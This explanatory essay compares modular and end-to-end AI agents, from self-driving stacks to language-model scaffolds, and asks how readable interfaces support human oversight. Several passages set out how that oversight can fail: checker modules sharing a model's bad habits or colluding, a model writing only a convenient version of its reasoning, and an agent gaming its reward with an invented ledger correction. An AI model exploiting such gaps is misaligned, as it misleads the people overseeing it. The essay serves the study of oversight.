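# Modular versus end-to-end AI agents: what inspectable parts add to oversight

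## Modules, interfaces and end-to-end training

An AI agent is a computer system that takes in information about its surroundings, chooses an action, carries it out and starts again from the result. Examples include a self-driving car and a program that reads a company's bank statements, queries its accounting software and corrects entries that don't match. Engineers can build an agent from modules, each with its own task, inputs and outputs, so that they can test or replace one without rebuilding the rest. They can also train a single system to go from raw input to action, in which case training determines the steps in between.

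The two approaches differ in what a person can inspect. An interface is whatever one module passes to the next, such as a list of objects, a text message or a vector of numbers. If the interface is readable, people can inspect it before the agent acts. How much control this gives them is in dispute, and the two fields with the most experience of readable interfaces have moved in different directions. Self-driving companies worked on modular systems for more than two decades before a decisive turn towards end-to-end networks, which Nebot and Berrio Perez (2026), in *The Era of End-to-End Autonomy*, date to 2024 and 2025. Developers of language-model agents, meanwhile, often build them from planners, workers and checkers that send each other text.

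### A pedestrian behind a van

The modular design for driverless cars, which engineers call the classical driving stack, has four stages: perception, prediction, planning and control. Stanley, the car that won the DARPA Grand Challenge, a desert race, in 2005, ran a pipeline of this type, and *A Survey of End-to-End Driving* (2020) uses it as a reference case. Autoware, an open-source driving system, publishes the contents of each of its interfaces. If a pedestrian steps out from behind a parked van as the car approaches, an engineer can follow the information about that pedestrian through the software message by message.

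Perception starts from camera images, radar and lidar, a sensor that measures distances with laser pulses. While the van still hides the pedestrian, the software has nothing to detect, but it does keep a grid map of the space around the car on which the area behind the van counts as a blind spot. Once the pedestrian comes into view, as Autoware's *Perception component design* describes, a detector produces an object with the class "pedestrian", and a tracker gives the object an ID and estimates its velocity. Prediction then adds the paths the pedestrian might take, each with a probability. (Autoware files prediction under perception; most accounts treat it as a stage of its own.)

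The planner receives a short record: a class, a shape, a position, a speed and some possible paths. Kapse (2026) points out in *End-to-End Learning vs. Modular Architectures* that detectors typically output only a box and a label, and drop the context of the scene. The record would omit, for example, that a pedestrian is looking at a phone, even if the camera image shows it.

Autoware's *Run Out* documents the module that determines whether the car must change its planned trajectory to avoid the pedestrian. The module projects the four corners of the car along its path, does the same with the pedestrian's more probable paths, and calculates when the two would occupy the same ground. If the predicted collision persists for a set time, which filters out noise in the predictions, the module inserts a stopping point into the trajectory some distance before the collision. A longer wait prevents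 false stops but also delays real ones.

The planning component sends control a trajectory, which is a sequence of points with positions, speeds and accelerations. According to Autoware's *Planning*, each planning module also publishes a message giving the reason for stopping, slowing or turning the vehicle. Control converts the trajectory into a target steering angle, speed and acceleration. Finally, the command gate limits abnormal values, such as a sudden change of steering, before the commands reach the vehicle.

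### An account to reconcile

A language model is a neural network that continues whatever text it receives. It cannot open a ledger on its own, so to turn it into an agent, developers write a scaffold. This is ordinary program code that calls the model repeatedly and gives each call a role, a context (the text the model works from) and tools such as a search function or a database query. Zhu and Cai (2026), in *From Language Models to World-Acting Systems*, call this layer the harness and include memory, retry logic and password handling in it. They argue that a benchmark score should be attributed to the whole configured system, since changing the available commands can change the results even when the underlying model stays the same.

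Reconciling an account means comparing a ledger with a bank statement and explaining every difference. One way to divide this work is to split the sequence of steps into consecutive stretches. In the running example of *Attention Tax, Handoff Tax* (Anchan and Sen, 2026), an agent handles one transaction per step and can pass a summary to a fresh copy of the model, which continues without the full history.

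Dividing by role is more common in discussions of oversight. The system in *Verification-Aware Planning for Multi-Agent Systems* (Xu, Mitra and colleagues, 2025) has a planner, workers, a verifier and a coordinator. It would handle the account roughly as follows. The planner splits the job into subtasks, such as "extract the March payments", "match them to ledger entries" and "list what is left over", and sets the name and format of each result. It also writes the acceptance checks in advance. Some are small programs, such as one that tests whether the matched and unmatched payments add up to the statement total. Others are plain-English instructions for a language model to judge by. Each worker gets its own instructions and the results it depends on, but never the overall task. The verifier then runs the checks. If any check fails, the subtask fails, and the coordinator has the worker try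 again, up to three times by default, before asking the planner for a new plan.

The interfaces here are text that anyone can read, but they can carry very little information. *Do More Agents Help?* (2026), a study of such workflows, reproduces the log of a team of agents answering a question about crocodile sightings in Florida. In that log, the solver sends the verifier an answer (11), a task number and one line of reasoning that names the database and the count. The message does not include the records behind the count.

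These systems also produce a second kind of readable text, the chain of thought, which is the reasoning a model often writes out before it answers or acts. Many agents cycle through reasoning, an action and the action's result. A planner might write that two payments look like duplicates and that it will query the bank record first. The chain of thought is faithful if the stated reasoning is what produces the action. Experimenters test this by changing the reasoning and watching what the agent does.

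### What end-to-end training does

A neural network is a long calculation with adjustable numbers called parameters. Training measures the error between the network's output and a desired output, then shifts each parameter slightly in the direction that reduces that error. In a classical stack, each learned module has its own error. Engineers train the detector against boxes that people drew around pedestrians, and the predictor against the paths that pedestrians later took.

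End-to-end training adjusts all the parts together, based on how good the final action was. If the car fails to brake when it should, the correction runs backwards from the brake command through planning and prediction to perception, changing parameters in each part.

A little notation shows what this does to the interfaces. Let perception turn the sensor input x into a signal z, and let planning turn z into an action a. The error L depends only on a. For a parameter θ inside perception, the correction follows from

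dL/dθ = (dL/da) · (da/dz) · (dz/dθ).

The formula depends on the signal z only through its effect on the action, not on what z means to a person. Suppose z begins as the distance to the pedestrian in metres, and the planner brakes when z falls below 15. If perception drifted to giving the distance in feet and the planner's threshold shifted to match, the car would brake exactly as before and the error would be the same. The same is true of any reversible recoding of z that the planner undoes. Perception could also mix into z an estimate of whether the pedestrian is about to run, and training will favour this if it improves the braking.

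An intermediate signal therefore keeps its human meaning only if something constrains it to. Engineers can freeze the perception module and train only the rest. They can follow the module with hand-written code that treats its output as metres. Or they can add a second error, so that training minimises L(action) + λ · L(objects), where L(objects) measures how far the signal departs from the true positions of objects and λ weights that error. This last method keeps the positions in the signal, but the signal can still carry other information. Such information is called leakage when it influences the action without being part of what a human reader is told. A later section covers the evidence for it.

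Without such an anchor, the internal boundaries blur. *A Survey of Deep Reinforcement Learning Algorithms for Motion Planning and Control* (2021) covers networks that learn to drive by trial and error, and concludes that end-to-end training leaves no clean break between the parts that extract features from the image and the parts that control the car.

### Four arrangements

Modularity is a property of a system's structure, and end-to-end is a way of training it, so a system can be both. Understanding AI's *Waymo and Tesla’s self-driving systems are more similar than people think* quotes an interview in which Dragomir Anguelov of the robotaxi company Waymo said, "You can still have modules and train things end-to-end." Four arrangements cover most of the agents in the debate.

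| Arrangement | What passes between the parts | What training adjusts |
|---|---|---|
| Separately trained stack | Outputs that people defined: objects, paths, a trajectory | Each learned module alone, by its own error |
| Language model in a scaffold | Text | Usually nothing further; the scaffold calls copies of a finished general model |
| Jointly trained modules with readable outputs | Learned vectors, with objects or text for people to read | All modules together, by the final action and often by extra errors on the readable outputs |
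| Single network | Nothing that a person must be able to read | The whole network, by the final action |

Autoware's default setup is a separately trained stack, but its parts need not be written by hand. Users can replace the rule-based planning modules with a learned planner, and the planning component's outputs keep the same form. The single-network approach goes back at least to ALVINN, which Kapse traces to 1989. ALVINN took in a camera image of 30 by 32 points and a coarser grid of laser distances, passed them through 29 hidden units, and produced a steering direction without making a list of objects at any stage.

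Most of the recent driving systems called "end-to-end" look little like ALVINN. Guan, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Planning-Oriented End-to-End Autonomous Driving*, find that many influential ones retain object queries, occupancy maps or other structured representations. They cite UniAD as a turning point. This research system still has parts for detection, tracking, mapping and prediction, but organises them all around the final plan. Guan and colleagues call such systems end-to-end because the planning objective ties the parts together. Waymo's present design, which has three jointly trained modules, is the same kind of system.

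Language-model agents can also combine modular structure with end-to-end training. Most scaffolds don't change the model's parameters, but *Dr. MAS* (2026) applies reinforcement learning (training by reward) to teams of agents with roles such as solver and verifier. The verifier must still end its message with "approve" or "reject", so the team keeps its modular structure while training changes the models inside it.

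### Bottlenecks and readouts

A readable list of objects can stand in two quite different places.

```
Bottleneck:   camera → perception → [list of objects] → planner → brake

Readout:      camera → network → brake
                          └────→ [list of objects]
```

In the upper line the list is a bottleneck, a readable interface that is the only path from input to action. If an engineer deletes the pedestrian from the list, the car drives on. In the lower line the list is a readout, which the network produces alongside the action, and the action need not depend on it. Deleting the pedestrian there changes the engineer's display, but the car may still brake. *Towards Safer Autonomous Driving in an Open World* (2026) describes end-to-end methods that learn extra tasks such as object detection and depth estimation, partly to make the system easier to interpret. Those outputs can be readouts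 even when they are accurate, so accuracy alone does not show whether the action depends on them.

True bottlenecks are less common than block diagrams suggest. Autoware's planner receives the list of objects, an unlabelled cloud of obstacle points, and the map of blind spots. Deleting the pedestrian from the list would leave the pedestrian's points in the cloud. Any bottleneck would be all of these messages together. Similarly, a model's later words depend on its earlier chain of thought, but the model can also act directly on the original request, which is in its context.

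*Omni-Decision* (2026) comes closer to a bottleneck for language-model agents. Its central record is a ledger of evidence. When a tool returns a result, a critic module first checks whether the result is sufficient. Only one component writes to the ledger, following fixed rules, and the planner chooses its next action from what the ledger contains.

### Four tests of oversight

"Oversight" covers several abilities that an agent's design can grant or withhold separately. Four questions pull them apart.

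A readable record is complete if it contains everything that influenced the action. In the account, the messages between planner, worker and verifier would have to include every consideration that affected the final report. The crocodile message shows how much a legible note can leave out.

The classical stack can help engineers locate the cause of a failure. Autoware's guide to the run-out module lists reasons why a car might not stop for someone, each of which an engineer can check: the object's class is missing from the list of classes to react to, the object is in a zone the settings exclude, the software cut the object's predicted path short, or the car was too close to stop and the settings discard collisions it cannot avoid.

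Real cases are harder, because people first have to agree on what failed. On 23 January 2026 a driverless Waymo car struck a child who had run out from behind a double-parked SUV near a school in Santa Monica. The child had minor injuries, according to the US road-safety regulator, NHTSA (2026). In a statement quoted by Education Week (2026), Waymo said the system detected the child immediately and braked from about 17 mph to under 6. Axios' *Feds investigating after Waymo robotaxi hits a child near a school* (2026) reports that, by the company's account, the car performed exactly as planned. NHTSA is investigating whether the car's intended behaviour was cautious enough for a school at drop-off time. In a stack like Autoware's, an engineer could examine that behaviour in the prototype module described in *Occlusion Spot*, which is designed to slow the car before a spot where a hidden pedestrian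 could dart out. The engineer can check whether the module was switched on and what speed it set.

A reviewer can test whether an intermediate output affects the action by correcting it and checking whether the action changes. Suppose the reviewer finds 1,540 in the worker's note where the bank statement has 1,450, and fixes it. If the final report changes to match, the note was on the path to the result. If the report stays the same, the next module was working from something other than the note, which was only a readout.

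Another test is whether a limit can be enforced. The command gate in Autoware's *Control component design* restricts sudden swerves regardless of what led the planner to command them. The equivalent for the account would be a few lines of code that block any correction above a certain sum until a person approves it. Enforcing such a limit requires no insight into the agent. A single network behind a command gate would pass this test but fail the other three, while a car with a detailed display of its surroundings might lack any enforceable limit on its steering.

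## The case for building agents from inspectable modules

Mobileye, which supplies driving systems to carmakers, defends modular design with an argument about rare failures. Some alignment researchers, who study how to make AI systems pursue what people intend, defend it for agents too capable for anyone to check as a whole. Their combined case has four premises, and each holds only if the agent meets a certain condition.

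1. Small tasks are easier to check than large ones. For this to help, someone must be able to cut the large task into pieces that really are small, and correct pieces must add up to a correct whole.
2. Readable interfaces expose intermediate mistakes. The messages must contain what the next module acts on, and the reader must be able to notice an error, including something left out.
3. Isolated modules cannot coordinate on a hidden aim. They must have no channel except the ones people watch. They must also not arrive at the same aim separately, for instance because they had the same training.
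4. A faulty module can be replaced alone. The meaning of its interface must stay fixed, so that its neighbours have not adapted to its quirks.

If all of this holds, people can oversee an agent one step at a time even when its overall behaviour is beyond them.

### Ruling out rare failures

Mobileye's *Compound AI* (2025) describes a design, also called "compound AI", with layers for perception, planning and actuation that engineers develop independently. It uses several kinds of sensor and some hand-written safety rules. *Autonomous decisions* (Shashua and Shalev-Shwartz, 2024) explains the choice through the bias-variance tradeoff from statistics. Bias is error that arises because a system's design cannot represent everything that matters. A planner that receives only a list of objects has some bias, since the list leaves things out. Variance is error that arises because a system has fitted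 its training examples too closely and copes badly with new ones. A network that goes straight from video to steering avoids the planner's bias but needs huge amounts of data to reduce its variance.

Mobileye accepts some bias to reduce the data it needs. Shalev-Shwartz and Mobileye's chief executive, Shashua, cite Waymo as evidence that the bias of an engineered system can be small enough for a safe driverless car. But Waymo now trains its modules jointly, so its record is better evidence for modular structure than for training modules separately.

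Shashua and Shalev-Shwartz also doubt that collecting data will be enough. Mobileye's target is one critical failure in 10 million hours of driving. Suppose an end-to-end car has reached one in a million hours and now fails only in 1,000 rare situations, each of which comes up once in a billion hours. A million cars driving an hour a day would together meet one such situation daily. To reach the target, engineers must fix 900 of them, which the two estimate would take around three years. That is too low even on their own assumptions, because each repair makes the next failure rarer. When 100 situations are left, the fleet meets one only every ten days. All 900 repairs would take about 2,300 days, or more than six years. They acknowledge that nobody knows how rare situations are distributed. A modular car would also fail in some rare situations.

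The mathematics behind Mobileye's position is older. In *On the Sample Complexity of End-to-end Training vs. Semantic Abstraction Training*, Shalev-Shwartz and Shashua (2016) ask how many examples it takes to show that a car almost never fails. ("Semantic abstraction" is their name for building a system from modules with a clear meaning.) If the acceptable failure rate is ε, testers need on the order of 1/ε examples. With far fewer, they would probably see no failures and could not tell an acceptable car from one twice as dangerous. Testers can avoid needing so many examples by finding several things that must all go wrong before a crash, measuring how often each one does, and multiplying those rates.

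Here is how that works for a pedestrian. Suppose the car hits someone only if its camera system and its radar system both miss the person, and the target is one double miss in 100 million encounters. The paper's statistical bound requires about 1.2 billion encounters without a failure to establish this for the car as a whole with 95% confidence. If the two systems fail independently, each needs to achieve only one miss in 10,000, since

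1/10,000 × 1/10,000 = 1/100,000,000.

By the same bound, about 150,000 encounters without a miss by either system are enough, which reduces the testing required by a factor of 8,000. Shalev-Shwartz and Shashua give a more extreme example, in which three conditions, each with a probability of about one in a million, give a combined bound near 10⁻¹⁸.

Everything depends on the word "independently". The exact formula is

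P(both miss) = P(camera misses) × P(radar misses, given that the camera missed).

Suppose that in one encounter in 100,000 a parked van hides the pedestrian from both systems until it is too late. Each system can still be within its limit of one miss in 10,000, but double misses now happen at least once in 100,000 encounters, a thousand times the target. This is also hard to test for, because engineers can only learn how the radar performs when the camera has failed from the one encounter in 10,000 where the camera fails. Confirming that the radar misses only one in 10,000 of those still takes on the order of 100 million encounters.

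Shalev-Shwartz and Shashua acknowledge that near-independence is a prior assumption, and they allow for a small amount of dependence by multiplying each probability by a factor such as 1.1. They also argue that a car is no more likely to miss a vehicle in a dangerous position than one elsewhere, because dangerous vehicles are close and easy to see. That is reasonable for a truck ahead on a motorway, but much less so for a child who runs out between parked cars, where the danger arises because the car sees the child late.

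The paper's proof also implies another limit. Failure probabilities multiply only when all the failures must happen together to cause a crash. If any one module can cause a crash by itself, the failure rates add up. The paper's bound is twice their sum, plus the chance that the system fails while every module works. Five such modules with a failure rate of one in 10,000 each give a bound no better than one in 1,000. Splitting a driving stack into perception, prediction, planning and control therefore doesn't make their failure rates multiply. Redundancy does, and Mobileye builds it in. In AnandTech's *An Exclusive Interview with Mobileye CEO Prof. Amnon Shashua*, Shashua describes one perception system that uses only cameras and another that uses only radar and lidar. A company could pair two end-to-end networks in the same way. The advantage of modules is that engineers can define and measure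 failure at each one, such as a missed pedestrian.

### Thinking in small pieces

Ought, a non-profit research lab, asked whether reasoning can be divided as well. Andreas Stuhlmüller described this idea, which he calls factored cognition, in Ought's 2018 talk *Factored Cognition*. A person receives a workspace containing one question. They can write notes, reply, or ask subquestions, which go to other people in their own workspaces. Each person sees only their own workspace and has a short time limit, such as 15 minutes, so nobody has time to build up private understanding. Whatever passes from one piece of work to another is therefore recorded.

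To reconcile an account this way, one person might compare a single payment with a single ledger line, without learning which company it belonged to. The person who asked for the comparisons would see only "match" or "no match" for each line. Stuhlmüller showed that such a tree of questions can in principle run any algorithm. It was not yet known whether people could find the right small steps for tasks that nobody knows how to write as an algorithm.

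The purpose was to train AI using a scheme that Paul Christiano, who was on Ought's board, had proposed under the name iterated distillation and amplification. A person with several assistants can answer harder questions than the person alone, so a model learns to imitate the whole group, and copies of that model become the assistants in the next round. The hope was that any bad result would have to come through a series of steps that people had endorsed. Stuhlmüller called that "far from a guarantee" of good behaviour, but a better starting point than training on results.

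In a correction he added later in comments, Stuhlmüller said that the trained model copies only the group's questions and answers, because the full tree of steps would be far too large to imitate. Each assistant is then an opaque neural network, and only the messages between assistants remain readable. To check what happens inside each network, he would rely on interpretability research.

### Supervising the process

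Ought's *The spectrum* (2022) later put the argument in more general terms. It contrasts supervising outcomes, which means adjusting a system by how well its results turn out, with supervising process, which means judging whether each step is the right one to take. Engineers had no earlier launches of the James Webb Space Telescope to go on, but they expected it to work because they understood its modules and its deployment plan.

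Ought gives two reasons to supervise a system's process rather than its outcomes. First, some outcomes arrive too late to train on, such as those of a forecast about the next thirty years or a policy with slow effects. Second, a capable system may learn to game the measure of success. An accounting agent rewarded for leaving no unexplained differences could invent a correction that makes the totals agree. A supervisor who approves each match between a payment and an invoice would have a chance to reject that correction.

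Module names alone do not provide this kind of supervision. Ought's example is MuZero, a program that plays Go, chess and shogi at expert level. It looks modular because it has separate networks for representing the board, predicting how it will change and evaluating positions. But its developers trained all three together for reward, so the "world model" need not describe the game in a way a person would recognise.

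Learning theory gives some support for supervising a system's steps rather than only its answers. *Sample Complexity of Autoregressive Reasoning* (2026) considers a learner that must discover a rule which a system applies many times in a row. If the learner sees every intermediate step, the number of examples it needs does not grow with the number of steps. If it sees only the final answer, the number can grow in proportion to the steps, though no faster. But *A Theory of Learning with Autoregressive Chain of Thought* (2025) constructs a case where learning from the final answer alone is easier. The single step is hard to learn, but after two steps the final answer is the same whichever rule is in use, so a learner that only has to predict the answer needs no examples. Supervising steps therefore saves data when the steps affect the result. These theorems are about learning the correct answer,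 and they do not establish whether anyone can tell an honest step from a misleading one.

Ought acknowledged that developers can almost always improve a modular system on any single measure by training all its parts together. Computer vision and language processing both moved to this end-to-end approach.

### Separate roles for planning and acting

Eric Drexler, a researcher at Oxford, divides AI systems into larger parts. In a 2018 talk, *Reframing Superintelligence*, he argued that the many specialised AI systems that already existed should change how researchers think superintelligent AI might arise. Under his proposal, comprehensive AI services, a collection of services could do everything people want from a general AI, without a single agent that pursues its own goals. Ought places the proposal halfway between process-based and outcome-based systems, because each service has a clear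 role but its developers can train it on results.

Drexler applied this to language models in *The Open Agency Model*. Some models propose plans, and others criticise and compare them. People provide the goals and guide the choice of plan. Separate systems then carry out the chosen plan in small steps, within a budget and a schedule, while others monitor the work. For a factory, one model might draft ten designs, another might look for safety problems, and a third might order only the parts for the approved design. A plan has to be in a form that another component can act on, so it cannot stay hidden inside the planner. Drexler adds, with caveats, that people may be able to read it too.

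Critics object that one of these components would have to be so capable that controlling it would raise the whole control problem again. Drexler answers that very capable models can fill any role, because safety comes from what each one is allowed to do and who checks it. This answer depends mostly on the modules not colluding. In an online exchange, Drexler argued that defectors make large conspiracies difficult even among people, and that conspiracy would be harder still among deliberately varied AI systems. But a typical scaffold calls the same model in every role, so it has little of this variety. If training has given that model a bad habit, the planner and the critic will both have it, and they can make the same mistake without communicating.

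Drexler thinks a single agent, rather than a set of modules, may be efficient and unproblematic for narrow tasks with fast decisions, such as driving and board games. He and Mobileye disagree about driving.

Language-model cognitive architectures apply similar reasoning to a single agent. Developers surround a language model with a memory, a planner and a routine for reviewing proposed actions, similar to the parts of a mind that psychologists describe. People state the goal in ordinary language, and the agent stores its plans and memories as text, so a reviewer can read and edit them or stop an action before it happens. Drexler makes a related case for "role architectures", in which language models play different parts in solving a problem. The alignment benefit depends on the model doing its important reasoning in that text. If it can work out a plan in a single call and write down only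 a convenient version, the memory will store, and the review routine will check, only that version. Later sections cover experiments on this problem, including tests of whether answering subquestions separately makes stated reasoning more faithful.

### What Ought's experiments found

Ought tested the idea on people before testing it on models. Ought (2018) ran seven one-hour sessions with seven to ten participants each, mostly on reading-comprehension questions from the SAT, an American university entrance exam. Questions that take one person five to ten minutes took at least one to two hours when the group divided them up. In a separate relay, each participant worked on a maths or programming puzzle for ten minutes and left notes for the next. They attempted 40 puzzles and solved four. Some participants could not have solved such puzzles alone, so it is hard to know how many of the failures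 came from dividing the work. But participants also introduced bugs, and their successors could not be confident that the earlier work was sound.

By the following year Ought had moved from producing answers to checking them. In the experiments described in Ought's *What we do and why* (2019), a judge had to determine a music reviewer's opinion of an album while reading no more than 650 characters. Two experts, one honest and one trying to mislead, had read the whole review. The judge could ask up to six questions, and a different judge settled each disputed answer in the same way. Ought reported that it had not shown the method to work reliably. In an extreme case, 22 people worked through 195 assignments over more than two months without reaching an answer.

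Ought (2020) tested a simpler version and got clearer results. Experts wrote true or false claims about film reviews and supported them with subclaims and quotations, while other experts added quotations as rebuttals. Judges saw one step of an argument at a time. Across 49 claims, accuracy was 55% when judges saw only the claim, 65% with one layer of argument and 69% with two, though the difference between one layer and two was not clear. These figures are favourable because Ought chose how to combine the judgments after seeing the data. Other choices lowered the two-layer accuracy to as little as 55%. With the method that gave 69%, judges accepted only one false claim but rejected 14 of the 24 true ones.

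The errors are more informative than the scores because they show why small, readable steps were still hard to check. The information that would have exposed the mistake was outside those steps. One false claim was that a film featured high-school activists. Quotations calling the characters "kids" and "brats" seemed to support it, but the reviewer meant immature adults. The full review made this clear in several places, but no short quotation did. Under one setting, judges accepted nine false claims, and in eight cases they overlooked that a key piece of evidence was missing.

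Experiments with language models went better. In *Iterated Decomposition*, Reppert, Rachbach and colleagues (2023) started with a simple program that picks a passage from a scientific paper and has a model answer questions using it. They then repeatedly looked for the step that failed and improved it.

| Task | Simple program | After decomposition |
|---|---|---|
| Describe the placebo in a medical trial | 25% | 65% |
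| Report how well participants kept to a treatment | 53% | 70% |
| Answer questions about language-processing papers | 38% | 69% |

The second task gives the clearest evidence that developers can find and repair a faulty module on its own. The program often wrongly reported that a paper had no information on how well participants had kept to the treatment. Reppert and colleagues traced all 51 of these errors to the step that selected the passage. Replacing that step raised accuracy from 53% to 61%, and giving the answering step worked examples brought it to 70%.

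The developers also learned from the execution records that they had misjudged which steps mattered. To determine whether a trial used a placebo at all, they had built a chain of steps that copied how a researcher would reason, listing each group of patients and looking for one on a placebo. The chain contributed almost nothing, and the improvement came from asking about every paragraph separately. A few keyword rules did nearly as well on this question as the whole decomposition, scoring 94% against 98%, but they scored only 10% on describing the placebo.

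Two features of the study limit what it can support. The developers always had the correct answers, so they were debugging a program and never had to judge answers that nobody could verify. And most of the gains came from helping a 2022 model use long documents, which is much less of a problem for newer models. An older test on GPT-3 by EleutherAI, a research group, shows a similar pattern. On nested arithmetic, the model scored 66% when it worked step by step and 15% when it answered directly. With two more levels of nesting, the step-by-step score fell to 17%, because one wrong step makes the final answer wrong.

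### Tasks that resist division

The most serious objection to this position is that some tasks cannot be divided. Stuhlmüller himself gave the example of a problem from halfway through a mathematics textbook. Someone who has worked through the first half has built up concepts and hunches that make the problem manageable. A hundred people with 15 minutes each have none of these, and that person could not easily write them down in a note.

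One reply is that the reader also learned the subject in steps, and that deciding how to divide a problem can itself be a subtask. That makes a division possible in principle, but it doesn't guarantee that anyone will find it with reasonable effort.

Ought's better reply is to divide only the checking. An end-to-end model can produce the answer by any method, and people then examine the answer in small pieces. For example, solving a Sudoku may take insight, but checking a completed one only requires looking at each row, column and box. For the textbook problem, readers could check a proof line by line without having come up with the idea behind it. Ought also thought it would be enough if most systems were largely process-based by the time AI transforms the economy, with small amounts of training on outcomes. It expected people to choose such systems for the highest stakes.

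This reply is convincing for proofs, puzzles and accounts, where there is a definite test for each line. It is weaker for long-range forecasts and policy advice, which Ought most wanted AI to help with. The evidence for a forecast is often spread out, as the film reviewers' opinions were, and the checking trees for even a one-page review grew too large to finish.

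## The case for end-to-end training

Tesla, like Ought, concluded that joint training performs better, and gave up a modular driving stack that its engineers had found easier to debug. Wayve, a London company that supplies driving software to carmakers, planned from the start to do without one. Both companies say that fixed boundaries between modules limit how well a car can drive. They also dispute that readable modules give people much control, and would rather judge a car by testing it as a whole.

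### From ALVINN to Tesla's version 12

End-to-end training is older than most of the modular stacks it is replacing. ALVINN, in 1989, was followed by DAVE in 2004 and NVIDIA's successor to DAVE in 2016, both of which learned to steer from camera images alone. According to Nebot and Berrio Perez, these early networks could handle only fairly simple driving, and the approach revived in the 2020s because large fleets of cars could supply millions of hours of recordings.

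Training now usually has two stages. The network first learns from recordings to predict what human drivers did with the wheel and pedals. This makes it drive naturally, but leaves it weak in situations that the recordings rarely contain or that people handle inconsistently. Engineers then train it with reinforcement learning on rare and simulated situations, rewarding wider safety margins, smoother driving and fewer human interventions.

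Alex Kendall, Wayve's chief executive, pitched a single driving network to investors in 2017. In Sequoia Capital's *How End-to-End Learning Created Autonomous Driving 2.0*, an interview from November 2025, he recalls hundreds of meetings in which people told him such a system would be unsafe or impossible to interpret. Opinion shifted after Tesla released version 12 of its Full Self-Driving software in 2024. Nebot and Berrio Perez say version 12 replaced thousands of lines of hand-written rules with one network.

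By June 2026, Tesla was running driverless robotaxis in Austin, Houston and Dallas and had shipped its self-driving software to 1.3 million vehicles, according to the head of its AI team (Elluswamy, 2026, *Building Foundational Models for Robotics at Tesla*). In July, Norihiko Shirouzu of Reuters reported that Wayve had raised $2.8 billion. In September, Wayve (2026) announced supervised rides in London with Uber. The same month, Mercedes-Benz agreed to put Wayve's software into production cars within two years, but as driving assistance, not autonomy (Popa, 2026, *Mercedes-Benz is putting a British AI driver into its production cars*). Much of the human oversight of end-to-end cars therefore still comes from someone in the driver's seat, who watches the road and can take the wheel. Waymo, which runs the largest driverless service of the three, says that pure end-to-end systems do not meet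 its safety bar, according to Axios' *Waymo says there's no AI shortcut to self-driving*.

### What a fixed interface costs

Both sides accept the complaint that modular systems lose information. Waymo keeps its modules, but its co-chief executive Dmitri Dolgov told Understanding AI that nobody can "enumerate a set of variables that are sufficient to be a good driver".

Errors also build up from one module to the next. Suppose a detector assigns a 60% probability to a roadside shape being a cyclist, but passes on only the word "cyclist". The prediction module assigns a 70% probability that a cyclist there would ride straight on, and passes on only that path. The planner receives one cyclist on one path and no probabilities, although the chance that both outputs are right is 0.6 × 0.7 = 0.42.

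Engineers can send the probabilities along too, as Autoware does with its predicted paths. Elluswamy accepts that this is technically possible but thinks it works poorly in practice. One likely reason is the number of combinations, since ten road users with three possible paths each have 3¹⁰, or 59,049, possible combinations of paths. In a jointly trained network, perception can pass on a weak sign of a cyclist without first deciding whether one is there, and planning can learn to slow down slightly in response.

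Companies also have commercial reasons to use end-to-end training. In Yoshida's *Has Waymo Gone End-to-End AI?*, Phil Koopman, an autonomous-vehicle safety expert at Carnegie Mellon University, points out that it lets them employ fewer people to label objects and fewer programmers to write the code that joins modules. He says end-to-end training takes much less work to get the first 90% of the system running, and calls it seductive for carmakers but dangerous for safety.

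### The puddle

Tesla's fullest case for end-to-end training is an October 2025 talk by Elluswamy (2025), in *A Peek into Tesla’s Autonomous Future*. He says Tesla used to build explicit modules "because it was so much easier to debug", but he found it hard to put human preferences into code. For example, a car approaching an obstacle can brake early and gently or late and hard. Passengers dislike both extremes, and the right point between them changes with the speed and the situation.

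His main example is a two-way road with a large puddle in the car's lane. The way round it is through the oncoming lane. A hand-coded planner would typically give each possible path a cost, for instance

cost = w₁ · (water driven through) + w₂ · (time in the oncoming lane),

and take the cheapest. Engineers have to set w₂ high, or the car will cross the centre line for trivial reasons. With a high w₂, though, it ploughs through every puddle. A human driver sees that the road ahead is clear and goes round. To reproduce that, w₂ would have to depend on how far the car can see, whether anything is coming and how deep the water looks, and the next odd situation would need its own adjustments.

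Elluswamy gives two more examples. In one, a Tesla waits for the last of several chickens to cross the road, even though the car was not going to hit it. In the other, the car backs up and drives around geese sitting still in the road. No programmer wrote a rule for either situation. In a post quoted by Teslarati's *Tesla VP explains why end-to-end AI is the future of self-driving*, he calls such choices "mini-trolley problems" and says that a network trained on human driving learns human values.

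The puddle example is a good argument against hand-written cost functions but a weaker one against modules. A learned planner that gets its input through a readable interface could also learn to drive around the puddle, as long as the interface reported the puddle and the view ahead. An interface that listed only vehicles and pedestrians would leave out both.

Learning the trade-off also makes it harder to challenge. With the hand-coded planner, a regulator can ask for w₂ and demand that the company raise it. A trained network has no such number, so the regulator must watch how the car handles many puddles and ask Tesla to retrain the network if the car takes too many risks. The number gives less control than it seems to, because nobody can tell from w₂ alone what a planner with dozens of interacting weights will do, but it gives the regulator and the company something definite to argue about.

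### How Tesla inspects its network

Elluswamy estimates that 30 seconds of video from all the cameras, along with the car's speed and route, amounts to about two billion tokens, or pieces of input. The network must turn these into two tokens, the next steering and the next acceleration. With so much input, it can easily learn the wrong reason for a correct action. In his 2026 talk, he gives the example of a car that brakes because tree branches are shaking. Mauricio Muñoz, a research engineer at AI Sweden, told Yoshida that end-to-end training encourages such shortcuts. He considers it "just short of impossible" to find where such a system went wrong.

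Tesla replies that the same network can produce much more than driving commands. Engineers can prompt it for the objects around the car, the traffic lights, the road boundaries and the occupied space, or ask it in plain language why it made a decision. It can also reconstruct the scene in three dimensions using a version of Gaussian splatting, which represents a scene as many small, soft-edged blobs. If a car parks too close to its neighbour, engineers can check the reconstruction to see whether the network estimated the gap incorrectly.

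All these outputs are readouts. In 2025 Elluswamy said that only the control actions matter in the car and that "everything else is auxiliary". By 2026 he was describing the outputs as something like reasoning traces, which help to produce the action and let engineers trace a wrong action to the reasoning that failed. That is a stronger claim, but he describes no test in which engineers changed the network's estimate of a gap to see whether the steering changed too. He says the model can write out its reasoning before it acts when a situation calls for it, though doing so every time would be too slow.

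Tesla's other method is to test the driving network in a simulated world, which doesn't require seeing inside the network. The company has trained a second network to generate this world. It takes the recent past and a driving action and produces what all eight cameras would show next. In one replay of an old failure, where the car had passed too close to a pedestrian, the newer version of the driving network starts to move over as soon as the pedestrian emerges from behind a parked car. Engineers can also alter a recording, for example by making a vehicle in the next lane cut across.

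Testing the driving network in a learned simulator measures its behaviour directly, and engineers can interpret the result without knowing how the network works internally. But the simulator and the network learn from the same recordings. If the fleet has never encountered a kind of event, it may be missing from both, and the test would not reveal the gap. Kendall says he believes that anyone with a perfect simulator has solved self-driving, and vice versa. If he is right, a fully reliable test of this kind is about as hard to build as the self-driving system itself.

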